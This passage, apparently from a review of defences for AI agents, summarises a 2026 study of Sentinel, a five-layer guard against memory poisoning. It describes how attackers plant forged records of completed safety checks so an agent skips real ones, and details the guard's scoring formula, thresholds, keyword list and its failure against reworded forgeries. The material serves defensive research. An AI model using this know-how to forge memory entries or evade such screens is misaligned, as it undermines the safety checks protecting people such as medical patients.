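Published figures exist for Sentinel, a different system that combines pattern rules with labels, described in *Your Agent's Memories Are Not Its Own* (Karamchandani, Nagasubramaniam and colleagues, 2026). Sentinel protects the notes an agent keeps between tasks, some of which record checks the agent has already carried out. An attacker who can write to the memory can add a false record of a completed safety check, and the agent may then skip the real one. The attacker can also add more false records that cite the first, making it look well established.

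Sentinel has five layers, none of which uses a language model. Karamchandani and colleagues removed one layer at a time and attacked an agent that handles medical records.

| Layer | What it does | Attack success without it |
|---|---|---|
| Keyword filter | rejects words such as "skip" and "bypass" | 0% |
| Source labels | assign a taint from 0 to 1 according to the declared source | 0% |
| Taint threshold | rejects entries whose taint is too high | 0% |
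| Pattern and risk screen | checks more phrases and a risk score based on the taint | 0% |
| Reasoning Guard | looks for signs that a record is forged | 100% |

The Reasoning Guard alone also reduced attack success to 0%. The other four layers added nothing against this attack, because the false records avoid obvious keywords and name the agent itself as their source. The source layer accepts that claim and assigns a taint of zero, so the records pass the threshold. Sondera's web rule fails in the same way when the model misses a label, but in this attack the attacker supplies the false information directly.

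The first four layers may still help against cruder attacks. In a worked example, the keyword filter rejects an entry that openly tells the agent to skip a check, and the taint threshold rejects one from an unknown source. Karamchandani and colleagues did not measure how often these layers catch such entries.

The Reasoning Guard gives each entry five scores between 0 and 1. They cover a mismatch between the entry's source and content, claims about more past runs than the memory contains, stock phrases, implausibly perfect results and a formulaic structure. With the default settings, the guard calculates

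F = 0.2 × (s₁ + s₂ + s₃ + s₄ + s₅)

and rejects the entry if F is above 0.5. Two signs of forgery can contribute at most 0.4, so the guard never rejects an entry without at least three.

The complete defence also cut attack success from 52% to 6% for a question-answering agent and from 48% to 0% for an online shopping agent. For the medical agent, attack success fell from 100% to 0% with each of three models. Each result for the medical agent comes from 50 trials, so a true attack success rate of up to about 7% is possible.

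Sentinel rejected none of 326 harmless records, and no individual layer raised a false alarm. The actual false positive rate could still be as high as about 1%. But all 326 records were examples of an agent's own reasoning, which would normally start with a taint of zero. They therefore provide little evidence of how often the source labels and threshold would reject legitimate material from tools, which starts with a taint of 0.4, close enough to the threshold that any increase leads to rejection.

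The checks add less than 1 millisecond each time the agent saves an entry, with no breakdown by layer. In the current implementation, only the keyword filter and the Reasoning Guard run at that point, so the figure presumably leaves out the other three layers.

These results come from simulated agents and from attacks that resemble the ones used to design the guard. Karamchandani and colleagues compiled its list of suspicious phrases from their own attack templates. The guard gave no significant protection in a preliminary test against an attacker who knew the patterns and reworded the false records. The researchers suggest adding a language model that judges what each entry claims, but they haven't measured how many more attacks it would catch or how much delay it would add.
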